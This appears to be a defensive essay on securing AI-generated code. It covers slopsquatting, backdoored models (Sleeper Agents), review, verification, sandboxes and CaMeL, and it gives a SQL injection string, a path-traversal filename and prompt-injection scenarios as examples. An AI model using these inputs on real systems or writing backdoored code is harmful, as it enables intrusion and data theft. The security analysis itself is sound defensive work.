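Models may also repeat the same secrets across applications. Hard-coded credentials, meaning passwords or keys written into the code, were a recurring finding in the Feature-Security Table study. Claude Code hard-coded the secret for login tokens in one of Andročec's applications. If a model used the same secret in a thousand applications, an attacker who read it in one could try it on the others.

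The study shows that models repeatedly write secrets into code, but not how often the same secrets recur. Anyone could find out by asking a model for a few dozen applications and comparing the secrets, and attackers have as much reason to do this as researchers do.

Models may also repeat their choices of package names. A model sometimes tells a program to install a package that doesn't exist. An attacker can upload malware to npm or PyPI under the invented name, and the next agent to invent the same name will install the malware. Lawfare, a publication on law and national security, points out that users would have to verify every package to prevent this, which defeats the purpose of vibe coding.

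The attack works only if models invent the same package names again. In *We Have a Package for You!*, Spracklen and colleagues (2025) took prompts that had produced invented packages and ran each one ten more times. In 43% of cases, the same name came back every time. The models in that study are now old, and newer ones may invent fewer names. An agent today would normally notice a missing package when the installation failed. But once an attacker has registered the name, the installation succeeds and the agent sees nothing wrong.

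### The model as a shared supplier

The same model can write many programs that share no code. A model that writes code for millions of people is part of the supply chain for all of that code, much as a popular package is for every program that installs it. If somebody tampered with the model, or a fault in its training led it to write less secure code, all of its users could receive worse code.

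Ken Thompson, one of the creators of the Unix operating system, described a similar problem in his 1984 lecture *Reflections on Trusting Trust*. He showed how to change a compiler, a program that turns source code into a form the computer can run, so that it added a secret password whenever it translated Unix's login program. Anyone who read the compiler's source code would see this change, so he made the compiler recognise its own source code too, and add both changes whenever it translated a new version of itself. He could then delete both changes from the source. Anyone who checked the source of the login program or the compiler would find nothing wrong, but every new copy of the compiler would still add the password. Thompson concluded that people cannot fully trust code they did not write themselves.

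A model is harder to inspect than a compiler because its behaviour comes from billions of numbers set during training, and no source code explains what it will do. Its output is ordinary source code, where a careful reader could find the secret password, but the owner of a one-off program usually doesn't read the code. Schneier expects attackers to also try to corrupt the AI systems that defend software, and warns that there may always be a "trusting trust problem".

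*Sleeper Agents* (Hubinger et al., 2024) describes models deliberately trained to have such a backdoor. They wrote secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and inserted vulnerabilities when it gave 2024. Standard safety training did not remove the behaviour. The experiment shows that a company could train and test a model in the usual ways and still release one with a backdoor, though it does not show that any commercial model has one.

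A model can also write worse code under certain conditions without anyone intending it. In 2025 the security firm CrowdStrike found that the Chinese model DeepSeek-R1 wrote code with severe vulnerabilities in 19% of cases under ordinary conditions, and in 27% when the prompt said the software was for use in Tibet. A test that never mentioned Tibet would have missed this increase, which CrowdStrike thought was probably an accidental effect of training.

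The agents that Sun and colleagues tested wrote less secure code when similar code in the project was insecure, even though no attacker had tampered with the models. This problem affects far more users than tampering does, and anyone who could add insecure examples to a project could exploit it deliberately.

One clear advantage of sharing a supplier is that the supplier can correct a recurring mistake for everyone. Kordonsky and colleagues suggest that AI companies test each risky feature separately and add a step that rewrites the code for logins, uploads and payments. This would improve every program their models wrote afterwards, but existing programs would keep their flaws until someone fixed them.

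### Which programs gain from being unique

The lawyer's script gains the most from being unique. Outsiders don't know it exists, can't send it requests, and have only a few minutes before it finishes. But most of that protection comes from running briefly on a private laptop, so a copy of a popular script would be nearly as hard to reach. The parts most exposed to attack are the library that reads the PDFs and the agent, which other people also use. A criminal could hide an instruction for a popular agent in a contract and send that contract to hundreds of law firms.

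Keeping a tool private gives it some protection, because outsiders cannot study its code or test it for flaws. But a dishonest employee or an intruder on the network can at least test it, and may have years to do so. Owners can also be wrong about whether a tool is private, as shown by the thousands of exposed items that Red Access found.

The public application gains the least from being unique. Scripts written for WordPress and other popular products won't work on it, and for a small site with little to steal, that may be enough to make attackers go elsewhere. But attackers can still probe the site and infer some of its likely flaws from its visible features. The protection will shrink further as AI makes it easier to examine sites one at a time. An owner who stores customers' data should still get a security review.

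## Checking code that no human will read

A careful security review by a person costs far more than having an agent write a short program, and the people who can do such reviews are short of time. Even software companies, which employ reviewers, no longer read everything their agents write.

### Why human review does not keep up

He, Agarwal and colleagues (2026), in *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review*, followed a software company whose technology chief told engineers in June 2025 to double their output with AI. By April 2026 they had roughly done so, and about 90% of pull requests carried the company's label for AI-written code. There were 3.1 times as many pull requests as in early 2025 but only 1.5 times as many people reviewing them, so each reviewer's load doubled. The company coped mostly by moving review to AI tools:

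| Share of pull requests | Early in the study | By the end |
|---|---|---|
| At least one person reviewed it | 89% | 68% |
| A person wrote a comment on it | 39% | 21% |
| An AI tool reviewed it | 19% | 84% |

The company did not have to undo a larger share of its changes afterwards. This is reassuring about faults that users notice, but it is little evidence of security. The bookkeeper's invoice page works for every honest client, so nobody would have a reason to undo it.

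Other groups report the same pressure. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) found that the median regular contributor to open-source AI projects on GitHub submitted 183% more code in the second quarter of 2026 than in early 2024. Over the same period, the rate of review comments in these projects fell to 36% of its earlier level on pull requests with traces of AI, and to 46% on the rest. In the survey for *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026), 77.8% of respondents said they had more pull requests to review after AI-written ones became common.

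Using AI to review code does not clearly make it easier to keep up with reviews. *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026) surveyed 2,590 people at a large software company, and those who used AI for reviews did not report less difficulty keeping up. However, the people with the most to review may have been the first to try the tools, which would hide a benefit.

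These are all professionals, whereas the owner of a one-off program usually works alone, and the mistakes can be tiny. *Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts* (Councilman, Fu and colleagues, 2025) describes generated programs that were supposed to change one setting in a system file. Some searched for lines starting with the setting's name but left out the equals sign that follows it, so they could overwrite any other setting whose name began the same way. To catch this, the owner would have to notice one missing character and understand why it mattered.

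### How a scanner traces input

Static analysis is cheap enough to run on every program. Many scanners work by tracing data from a source, where an outsider's input enters the program, to a sink, an operation that is dangerous if an outsider controls it. Suppose the bookkeeper's site also lets staff search for a client by name:

```
name  = request.get("client")                                   # source
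query = "SELECT * FROM invoices WHERE client = '" + name + "'"
database.run(query)                                             # sink
```

The scanner has a list of known sources and sinks. It follows the value of `name` into `query` and then into `database.run`, and raises an alert because nothing on the way makes the text safe. The alert is correct because someone who types `' OR '1'='1` into the search box changes the command so that it returns every client's invoices. If the program sends the name to the database separately from the command, the database treats it as plain data and the scanner raises no alert.

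The invoice page also takes input from the visitor, in the form of the invoice number in the address. But looking up an invoice by number is a safe operation, so the input never reaches a sink. The fault is that the page doesn't check who owns the invoice, and nothing in the code shows that it should. An online shop could use the same code to show its products, and it would be correct there because every customer may see every product.

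A programmer can add a rule to the scanner, for example that every call to `find_invoice` needs an ownership check, but someone who knew to write that rule could have asked the agent for the check in the first place. Rule-based tools find only what somebody has programmed them to find, and they miss flaws that depend on who is allowed to do what. In *Evaluating LLM Security Review Agents with Operationally Sourced Ground Truth*, Khurana and Liman-Tinguiri (2026) give these limits as a reason for trying AI reviewers at their company, Airbnb.

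### Broken by Default

Scanners also miss some flaws that involve no hidden policy. *Broken by Default* (Blain and Noiseux, 2026) looked for such flaws in 3,500 programs, 500 from each of seven models, written for tasks that invite security mistakes. It examined them with COBALT, a tool that combines searches for suspicious patterns with Z3, a solver that searches for values that satisfy every condition in a set.

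One common mistake was the line `malloc(n * sizeof(int))` in the language C, which reserves four bytes of memory for each of `n` numbers. In 32-bit arithmetic, a result that reaches 4,294,967,296 starts again from zero, like a car's mileage counter. Z3 searched for a value of `n` that would trigger this, and found one:

```
n               = 1,073,741,825
n × 4           = 4,294,967,300
after wrapping  = 4 bytes
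```

The program would reserve room for one number and then write more than a billion, overwriting whatever else was in memory. An attacker can sometimes use such an error to take over a program.

COBALT reported at least one vulnerability in 55.8% of the 3,500 programs. The rate ranged from 48.4% for Gemini 2.5 Flash to 62.4% for GPT-4o, and from 25% for cryptography tasks to 87% for integer arithmetic tasks. For 1,055 of the findings, Z3 supplied values that trigger the fault, and Blain and Noiseux call these findings formally proven to be exploitable.

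That is too strong, because Z3 could assign `n` any value. The proof shows that some value causes an overflow, but not that an outsider could make the program use it. If `n` is the number of clients on the bookkeeper's list, it will never reach a billion. Most current computers would also do this multiplication in 64 bits, where the value above causes no overflow. Blain and Noiseux did attack seven programs of their choice, and six of the attacks worked. In one, a SQL injection extracted every record in a test database.

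They also compared COBALT with six other tools on an earlier set of 250 programs, 90 of which had a flaw proven with Z3. CodeQL, the scanner used to build the Feature-Security Table, flagged none of the 90. The other five tools together flagged two, and only because those programs also used an unsafe function for joining text.

CodeQL's overflow rules generally look for a path from an outsider's input to the risky calculation, and a short function with no program around it may not have one. The experiment therefore can't show whether CodeQL missed 90 flaws or correctly ignored 90 calculations that nobody had shown an outsider could reach. It also treats COBALT's findings as the truth, which guarantees that COBALT comes first, and Blain and Noiseux founded the company behind COBALT. The result is still a good reason not to trust a clean scan of C code, but it matters less for a website in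 Python or JavaScript, which rarely reserves memory by hand.

Asking the models for secure code barely helped. On the 50 tasks of the earlier set, the share of programs with a finding fell from 64.8% to 60.8%. These models are older than the ones that improved a lot after a reminder in the Last Secure Code Benchmark.

The models did better at reviewing code than at writing it securely. Blain and Noiseux gave 89 of the programs with proven flaws back to the models that had written them and asked for a security review. The models recognised the flaw in 70 of them (78.7%). GPT-4o recognised 12 of its 18, and Mistral Large recognised all 17 of its own. But every program in this test was flawed, so a model that labelled all code vulnerable would have scored 100%.

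### False alarms

Reviewers that condemn too much are a real problem. Jin and Chen (2026), in *Are LLMs Reliable Code Reviewers?*, took more than 700 small programming tasks, each with one correct and one faulty solution, and asked five models whether each solution met its description. They asked first for a plain yes or no, and then also for an explanation and a corrected version. The table shows the three commercial models' results on HumanEval, a set of short Python tasks:

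| Model | Correct code rejected: yes/no only | Correct code rejected: with explanation and fix | Faulty code accepted: yes/no only | Faulty code accepted: with explanation and fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 26.2% | 73.2% | 2.4% | 0.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 26.2% | 36.0% | 2.4% | 0.6% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 25.6% | 34.1% | 8.5% | 5.5% |

Asking for an explanation and a fix made the models stricter with good and bad code alike. Across all the tests, in almost half of the wrongful rejections the model claimed an error in the program's logic, often without giving an input that would trigger it. In another 14%, the model relied on a requirement it had invented. The models were judging whether programs work, not whether they are secure, and the models are old, so today's rates may be quite different. But an owner who can't read code will naturally ask for an explanation and a fix, and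 in these tests that was the worse way to ask.

Suppose 30 of 100 programs have a flaw, and a reviewer recognises 79% of the flawed programs and wrongly rejects 26% of the sound ones. The owners get 24 correct warnings and 18 false ones, and six flawed programs pass. If the reviewer wrongly rejected 73% of the sound programs, the owners would get 51 false warnings.

Letting the agent make every suggested change is risky, because needless changes can break a program or create a vulnerability, as one suggested in a report to curl would have. Jin and Chen suggest checking a complaint by running tests on both the original and the "corrected" version. The equivalent for security is to make the reviewer demonstrate an attack, such as logging in as one client and opening another's invoice. The audit of 200 live applications discarded many reports this way.

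### A test on Airbnb's own flaws

Khurana and Liman-Tinguiri tested AI reviewers on vulnerabilities that Airbnb had already fixed. Outside researchers, hired testers and Airbnb's own engineers had reported these vulnerabilities, so they are closer to what a reviewer would meet in practice than planted errors are.

The study gave an agent two tasks. In the first, it reviewed the code change that had introduced a flaw. In the second, it searched the code as it stood just before the fix, starting from a list of files. The agent could read files, list folders and search for file names, but had no information about the flaw. A separate model then compared the agent's findings with the original report of the flaw and decided whether acting on them would have largely solved the problem.

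The table gives the share of known flaws that each model found. The brackets contain 95% confidence intervals, which are wide because there were few cases.

| Model | Reviewing the change (40 cases) | Searching existing code (49 cases) |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 57% (42–72%) | 67% (53–79%) |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 30% (18–45%) | 69% (56–81%) |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 18% (9–32%) | 45% (32–59%) |

Most of the differences between models could be due to chance. The researchers ran each test once. They had adjusted the instructions on the same cases, although this changed the rates very little. GPT-5.5 judged the findings, including its own, and nobody checked its verdicts against human ones at scale.

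The records of what the agents did are more informative than the ranking. Opus 4.7 opened no files for 12 of the 40 changes because it decided from the change alone that the code was harmless. These were mostly small changes, such as a new setting or a one-line edit, where mistakes about permissions are easy to make. All three models explored about twice as much when they searched existing code than when they reviewed a change. The owner of a private tool should therefore ask for a review of the whole program after each change, which is practical when the program is short.

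In one case, Sonnet 4.6 described a piece of code as an unconventional approach, while GPT-5.5 read the same code and worked out that anyone could use it, without logging in, to carry out a privileged operation on behalf of any user. Sonnet 4.6's review alone would have given the code's owner no reason to worry.

All three models consistently missed dependencies with known vulnerabilities, which a tool like Dependabot can find. They also consistently missed cases where a program revealed data meant only for internal use, since nothing in the code marked that data as private. Khurana and Liman-Tinguiri suggest giving reviewers a company's own records of which data is sensitive. The bookkeeper could likewise give a reviewer one rule, "Clients may see only their own invoices", to check the page against.

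The study did not measure false alarms. When Sonnet 4.6 missed the known flaw in existing code, it still reported an average of five other problems. In one case it listed eight, covering missing permission checks on five related parts of the same service. Khurana and Liman-Tinguiri think such findings could all be genuine, but did not check.

### Two reviewers with overlapping blind spots

Adding a second reviewer helps only if it finds what the first one missed. Suppose a program has 100 flaws and each of two reviewers misses 20. If the second reviewer is no worse on the first one's misses than on other flaws, it also misses 20% of those 20, so four flaws get past both. If the two reviewers find the same things difficult, the second might miss 60% of the 20, and 12 flaws get past both. That is three times as many, although neither reviewer has become any worse. In general:

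```
missed by both = missed by the first × share of those that the second also misses
```

Song (2026), in *When Does a Second Model Help?*, compared two reviews by the same model with reviews by two different models. Claude Opus 4.6 produced 30 texts and programs, each with five planted errors. In one comparison, two separate reviews by Claude together found 64 of the 150 errors (42.7%), while one review by Claude and one by OpenAI's GPT-5.4 together found 85 (56.7%).

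In the mixed pair, Claude missed 94 errors. GPT-5.4 missed 57% of all the errors but 69% of those 94, which left 65 that neither found. If the misses had been unrelated, they would have both missed about 54. Some of the overlap may have arisen because certain errors are hard for any reviewer to find.

The advantage of mixing models is less certain than it appears from the headline figures. It may exist only because GPT-5.4 is a better reviewer than Claude. Two reviews by GPT-5.4 found 76 of 145 errors and the mixed pair found 82, a difference that could be due to chance. The result also varied between runs, with mixed pairs finding 45–57% of the errors and pairs of Claude reviews 30–43%, so the published comparison uses the best pair of each kind. The scoring may also have been unfair to Claude, because software matched the findings to Korean descriptions of the errors and 20 of Claude's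 30 reviews in the main run were in English.

Only ten of the 30 items were programs, and the rest were tutorials and scripts for talks. The planted errors were general mistakes, such as wrong facts and missing functions, rather than security flaws. On the programs alone, Claude scored higher than any of the other models when reviewing its own work in a fresh session.

False alarms would also add up. Only about 30% of each reviewer's findings matched a planted error, though some of the others may have been real errors that nobody planted.

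Song doesn't report what a review cost, and neither do Khurana and Liman-Tinguiri. In the invoicing example, the break-even price was $5.50 per program. A model could probably read a few hundred lines for less than that, but checking the false alarms might cost more than reading the code.

For a one-off program, a fresh review by the model that wrote it is a sensible minimum, and a second strong model is worth adding if the program holds other people's data. A cheaper second model may not help. In Song's experiment, the lightweight Gemini 2.5 Flash scored no higher than Claude did on its own.

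### Proving that a program meets its specification

Scanners and reviewers look for flaws and can always miss one. Formal verification uses mathematics to prove that a program meets a specification, a precise statement of what it must do. *Beyond Type-checking* (2026) divides the work into three steps: a model turns the user's request into a specification, writes code to meet it, and produces a proof that the code does so.

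Dafny, a programming language for this purpose, has a verifier that checks the proof automatically. Suppose the bookkeeper charges a fixed fee for each month that a payment is late:

```
method LateFee(months: int, fee: int) returns (total: int)
  requires months >= 0              // what the code may assume
  ensures total == months * fee     // what it must deliver
{
  total := 0;
  var i := 0;
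  while i < months
    invariant 0 <= i <= months
    invariant total == i * fee      // a step in the proof
  {
    total := total + fee;
    i := i + 1;
  }
}
```

The lines with `requires` and `ensures` are the specification. The `invariant` lines are hints for the verifier, and state facts that must hold before and after every pass through the loop. At the start, `total` and `i` are both zero, so `total == i * fee` is true. Each pass adds `fee` to `total` and 1 to `i`, so it stays true. The loop stops when `i` equals `months`, so `total` must then equal `months * fee`. This proof covers every combination of months and fees, while a test would check only a few.

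Writing such proofs used to take specialists, but models are now good at it. *AxDafny* (Breen, Letson and colleagues, 2026) presents a system in which a model receives a specification and writes the code and the proof hints. Software then checks that the model has not removed any part of the specification or used commands that tell Dafny to accept a claim without proof. If Dafny rejects the program, the system returns the error messages to the model, which tries again, up to 20 times. A second model looks for subtler cheating, such as redefining a condition so that it is always true.

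The system produced verified programs for 56.4% of 250 programming competition problems, compared with 11.6% for a single attempt by GPT-5.5. The system's success rate was 75% on the easy problems and 28% on the hard ones. Proof work on larger software is also taking less effort. *CompCert4Lean* (2026) describes how coding agents working in parallel moved a verified C compiler to the proof language Lean in six weeks.

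A verified program can still be too slow or use too much memory to be useful. Breen and colleagues translated their 127 verified solutions to the easy and medium problems into Python and ran the original competition tests. None gave a wrong answer, but only 38 passed. The other 89 ran out of time or memory, partly because the translation slowed them down and partly because the specifications set no limit on speed.

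### Letting the user check the specification

Breen and colleagues gave their system the specifications, but the owner of a one-off program has only a request in ordinary language. Councilman and colleagues designed a system called Astrogator for this situation. It checks programs in Ansible, a language people use to set up computers remotely by installing software, copying files and creating accounts.

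Even a simple request can be ambiguous. "Copy a file from /path/a to /path/b" could mean copying within the remote computer, or between it and the computer that sends the instructions. Councilman and colleagues meant the first, but all six models they tried wrote code to send the file from the controlling computer. Astrogator uses a formal query that resembles English but has only one meaning:

```
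move file from remote "/scratch/file.txt" to remote "/home/user/data.txt"
```

A model is eventually meant to translate the request into such a query, which the user will then confirm. Astrogator then converts the query and the generated program into descriptions of how each would change the computer's files, packages and accounts, and compares the two descriptions. A hand-made knowledge base supplies details that the user may not know, such as the exact name of a package on each operating system.

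Councilman and colleagues tested Astrogator on 1,260 generated programs for 21 tasks. They ran the programs on virtual machines to find out which were correct:

| | Accepted | Rejected |
|---|---|---|
| 334 correct programs | 277 (83%) | 57 (17%) |
| 926 incorrect programs | 70 (8%) | 856 (92%) |

About one in five of the accepted programs was therefore wrong. Of these 70 programs, 61 would have met the query if an extra assumption had been true of the test machines. For example, a program that copied a file from the wrong computer would work if both computers held the same file. Astrogator lists such assumptions so that a user can object, but the experiment did not use these lists. Another seven programs did something extra and harmful, such as overwriting a file that they were supposed to create only if it was missing.

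The models were weak by today's standards, so a current model would probably write fewer incorrect programs for Astrogator to catch. More importantly, the researchers wrote all the queries themselves, so the experiment does not show whether ordinary users can recognise a wrong query. The method also depends on Ansible's narrow purpose. Councilman and colleagues doubt that a readable query language could cover everything people do in a general-purpose language like Python.

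### Who writes the specification

For the bookkeeper's page, the specification might start with this rule:

```
if the page shows invoice i to user u, then u owns invoice i
```

The original page would fail, but a page that never shows anything would pass, so the specification needs a second rule that a logged-in owner can see the invoice. It probably needs others about staff and accountants. *How Powerful are LLMs in Generating Formal Program Specifications?* (2026) notes that writing a precise specification takes expert knowledge and often more effort than verifying the code.

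Models can write specifications, but "verified" may then mean very little. In *Verified but Vacuous*, Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026) repeated an earlier team's method, in which a model writes a solution in Dafny and then translates it into Python. Dafny accepted 99.1% of the programs that Claude Opus 4.7 wrote for the HumanEval tasks. Of those, 94.7% had no `ensures` line, so Dafny had checked basic matters, such as whether the program would finish, but no general statement of the right answer. Only 1.9% had an `ensures` line that referred to the separate specification. A few of the others may have stated something useful in another form.

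Requiring a program's proof to refer to the specification helps, but it cannot fix a weak specification. Vempaty and colleagues give the example of a program that should return the largest number in a list. If the specification requires only that the result be zero or more, a program that always returns zero passes. Their system enforces the proof requirement, but 11.5% of its verified programs on one set of tasks and 14.8% on another still failed tests that the system had not been given.

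A model that sees faulty code before it writes the specification may write the fault into the specification. *Are LLM-Generated Formal Specifications Faithful to Their Requirements?* (2026) gave models a written requirement together with a program that violated it. The models produced a valid specification that matched the requirement for only about a quarter of these programs. Some specifications matched the faulty program instead, so a verifier would have approved that program. An agent should therefore write the specification before the code.

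*AfterVibe* (2026) works in the opposite order, without formal proof. It recovers a plain-language specification from a finished vibe-coding conversation and counts it as correct if a model can use it to write an equivalent program. This is useful for rebuilding software later, but it would not expose the missing ownership check in the invoice page. If the specification also lacked the ownership rule, the page written from it would lack the check too, and the two pages would count as equivalent.

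Councilman and colleagues argue that only the user can confirm that a specification matches what they want. The bookkeeper can easily approve the rule that clients see only their own invoices, but would find it harder to notice that the rule is missing from a list. In the audit of live applications, more than half of the flaws came from a rule that the user had not mentioned and the agent had not supplied. Livshits (2026), in *LLMs + Security = Trouble*, adds that people who vibe code tend to accept every change by default, so they are likely to approve specifications the same way.

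Proof is therefore more promising for shared components than for whole one-off programs. Experts could write and check one specification for a PDF reader or a login system, and every generated program could then use the verified version.

### What a clean result is worth

Livshits also doubts that AI reviewers can make generated code safe. The most valuable vulnerabilities often lie behind a long chain of unlikely conditions, and a program can run in far too many ways for anyone to try them all. A defender stops when the time or money runs out, so finding no vulnerability often means only that the review didn't reach one. An attacker can concentrate on one target, keep trying, and use a stronger model that the defender doesn't have. Next year's models may also find vulnerabilities that today's models cannot.

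The invoicing example shows how weak the evidence is. Suppose 3,000 of 10,000 different sites have a serious flaw, and a review finds 69% of the flaws, Sonnet 4.6's rate in Airbnb's existing code, with no false alarms. It finds 2,070 and misses 930, so 7,930 sites get a clean result and 12% of those are still vulnerable. A clean result therefore lowers the chance of a flaw considerably, from 30% to 12%, but is far from a guarantee.

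Attackers also have limited budgets, however. In the earlier example, an attacker who paid $5 per site and gained $50 per break-in made a profit. If the owners repaired every flaw that the review found, the attacker would still spend $50,000 but could break into only 930 sites, worth $46,500, and so would lose money. The remaining flaws would probably also cost more to find, since the review would have removed the easy ones. This is compatible with Livshits's argument that a later attacker may succeed by putting in more effort, since effort costs money.

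This protection lasts only while examining a site remains expensive. If it cost $1 per site instead of $5, the same attack would make $36,500. The lawyer's script will have finished running long before that happens, but a website that stays online needs another review whenever much better models appear.

Livshits would prefer to prevent certain flaws by applying fixed rules while models generate the code. Such rules could force a program to check the bounds of every list or to clean any text before displaying it, but they could not supply an ownership rule that nobody had written down.

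Deterrence also fails when a single site is valuable. If breaking into the bookkeeper's site were worth $1,000, an attacker could spend up to $93 examining it after the review and still expect to profit. The owner of such a site should assume some flaw remains and limit what an intruder could reach, for instance by running the program in a sandbox.

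## Limiting what a generated program can do

Some generated programs will have flaws even after a good review. An owner can limit the damage through containment, which means restricting what a program can reach while it runs. Containment works even when nobody knows what is wrong with the code, so it suits programs that nobody reads. It also limits damage from malicious code in a dependency and from the agent's mistakes.

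### A script that renames photographs

Suppose the secretary of a sports club has 400 photographs with names like IMG_0412.jpg. A page on the club's website gives a new name for each one, and an agent writes a script to apply them:

```
table = read_table(fetch("https://club.example/matches"))
for photo in files_in("Photos/2026"):
    rename(photo, "Photos/2026/" + table[photo.name])
```

The script runs with the secretary's permissions, so it can change any of the secretary's files. Someone who can edit the web page could give one photograph the new name `../../Documents/accounts.xlsx`. Each `..` means "go up one folder", so on a Mac or Linux computer the script would replace the secretary's accounts with a photograph. Malware in a dependency, such as the malware in LiteLLM, could collect saved passwords and send them anywhere.

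Each of these limits removes a different harm:

| Limit | Setting for this script | Harm it prevents |
|---|---|---|
| Folders | Only Photos/2026, plus read access to Python's own files | Overwriting the accounts or reading other private files |
| Network | Only club.example | Sending data to any other site |
| Credentials | No passwords or keys | Logging in to other services as the secretary |
| Time and memory | One minute and 500 MB | Freezing the computer with an endless loop or an enormous page |

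The folder and network limits depend on each other. If the script could read the whole disk but contact only club.example, whoever controlled that site could still receive the secretary's private files.

Some scripts need a password to work. Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code describes a way to supply one without exposing it to the script. The script gets a placeholder, and a separate program that relays its web traffic inserts the real password only in requests to sites the user has chosen. Malware in the script could still misuse the account on those sites, but it couldn't steal the password.

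These limits do not protect the photographs themselves. If the page gives two photographs the same name, the second replaces the first. Limiting the script to a folder can't prevent this, because the script needs to write to that folder.

This kind of damage is common in public complaints about agents. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) collected 290 reports of agents misusing files, including one in which an agent deleted files it was supposed to rename. Of the cases with real or demonstrated harm, 42% involved files outside the project folder, so restricting agents to that folder would not have helped in the rest. In 40% of the cases where the outcome was known, the user could not fully recover. People don't report uneventful sessions, so these figures can't show how often agents cause harm.

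Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, a file system that keeps an agent's changes separate from the real files until the user accepts them. It also shows the agent what each command changed and lets it undo those changes. Agents noticed and undid the damage in eight of 11 tests with hidden destructive side effects. In the other three, the changes looked to the agent like part of the job, but the user could still reject them. For the secretary, a copy of the folder would work nearly as well. Neither method can undo a leak, so the user needs to limit which private files the script can read before it starts.

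### Sandboxes, containers and virtual machines

Several kinds of barrier can enforce these limits:

| Mechanism | What the program gets | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|
| Operating-system sandbox | The user's own computer, minus whatever the rules forbid | A flaw in the operating system's core can let the program out |
| Container | Its own set of files, plus any folders the user adds | It normally shares the same core |
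| Virtual machine | A simulated computer with its own operating system | It uses more memory and takes longer to start |
| WebAssembly | Memory to calculate with, plus any functions the host supplies | Many existing libraries do not run in it |
| Permissions for each task | The folders, sites and commands that one piece of code requests | The code needs a special language or tools |

A sandbox is enough for the renaming script, since it starts instantly and the files are already there. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends isolated machines, such as virtual machines, for services that run many people's generated code, with separate machines for users who must not share data. A stronger barrier doesn't make up for settings that allow too much access. If the secretary gives a virtual machine access to the whole Documents folder, the script can still overwrite the accounts.

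Granting permissions separately for each task is the most precise option. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that writes its code in Scala, a programming language whose compiler can track which parts of a program use which permissions. The code requests access to one folder, site or command at a time. Each permission ends with the block of code that requested it, and the compiler rejects code that would keep the permission for later. The compiler also lets code process secret files but prevents it from printing or sending their contents.

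Odersky and colleagues tested this on a project with a folder of secrets. Without the protection, the model MiniMax M2.5 revealed secrets in eight of 11 tasks that asked for them directly or under a pretext, and Claude Sonnet 4.6 did so in two. With the protection, neither model revealed any, even in 120 further trials with planted instructions, and the agents completed ordinary tasks about as often as without it. However, the guarantee doesn't cover other programs that the Scala code starts, so they recommend adding a sandbox.

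### What coding agents enforce by default

The leading agents have different sandbox defaults. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex runs commands in an operating-system sandbox, usually limited to the project folder, with network access off. Claude Code's sandbox is off by default and works on Windows only with a Linux layer. Zhong and colleagues found that Cursor's sandbox was on by default, Gemini CLI's and GitHub Copilot's were optional, and OpenCode had none.

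Even with its sandbox on, Claude Code lets a script read almost any file on the computer, including those containing passwords and keys, unless the user forbids it. The script can write only to the working folder, a temporary folder and any others the user has added. No sites are permitted at first, but once the secretary approves club.example, the script could send that site any file it can read. Anthropic also warns that permitting a broad site such as github.com could allow leaks, because anyone can have an account there.

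Some agents offer to rerun a command outside the sandbox if it fails inside. This is useful because sandboxes often block legitimate work, but it gives an unknown program full access just after it has tried to do something forbidden. Claude Code has a strict setting that removes this option. By default, Claude Code also runs commands without the sandbox if the sandbox cannot start, but the user can change this in another setting.

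The rules on an agent's tools for reading and editing files do not apply to a script, which opens files directly. In 77 of the 290 reports, the agent bypassed such rules, or could have, by using an ordinary command. For one-off code, the sandbox therefore matters far more than those rules.

### Approval fatigue

Without a sandbox, the usual protection has been to ask the user for approval before each risky step. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approved 97% of these requests. Most of the commands were probably harmless, so the approval rate alone does not show that users were careless.

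Anthropic ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. During each session, it replaced one request with a clearly dangerous command that would not actually run. Only 13.6% of the testers rejected it. Testers rejected about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more requests. A classifier model that judges each action before it happens blocked 89% of the same commands.

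Anthropic was promoting the classifier and doesn't report how often it blocked harmless commands. The testers also risked less than people working on their own files, so 13.6% may be too low for ordinary users. This lower risk doesn't easily explain the decline during a session, which looks like fatigue.

Since 14 August 2026, the classifier has replaced most requests in new Claude Code sessions on individual and team plans, unless the user chose otherwise. It reviews commands better than a tired person does, but it still has to predict their effects, while a sandbox restricts those effects directly. An owner can use both, but by default Claude Code now uses the classifier without the sandbox.

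Generated scripts make informed approval especially hard. A request to run `python rename.py`, for example, doesn't show which files the script will change. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026), a small study of permission requests, found that 13 of 16 participants used "Always Allow" just to stop the requests. Participants granted limited permissions, such as access to one folder, 3.5 times as often when the software offered that option.

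Sandboxes also reduce the number of approval requests, because commands that stay inside the limits don't need approval. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) cites Anthropic's figure of 84% fewer requests in Claude Code. Users are more likely to pay attention to the requests that remain.

### Tracking where data came from

A sandbox can let a program send email, but it can't distinguish an address supplied by the user from one supplied by an attacker. CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), tracks where the address came from. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) calls it the first defence against prompt injection he has seen that claims strong guarantees.

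Suppose the secretary asks an agent to email the photographs to the club's treasurer, whose address is on the website. In CaMeL, one model reads only the secretary's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python. A second model, here called `reader`, extracts facts from untrusted text but cannot take any action itself. The plan might look like this:

```
page    = fetch("https://club.example/contacts")         # source: web page
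address = reader("Find the treasurer's address", page)   # source: web page
photos  = files_in("Photos/2026")                        # source: private files
send_email(to=address, attach=photos)                    # policy check
```

An attacker could hide an instruction in the page that makes the second model return the wrong address. But the attacker can't add a step to the plan, because the model that wrote it never read the page. An interpreter runs the plan line by line and records where each value came from and who may read it. Before sending the email, the interpreter checks a policy, such as one that allows private files to go only to addresses the user has typed or saved. This address came from a web page, so the interpreter stops and can ask the secretary to confirm it.

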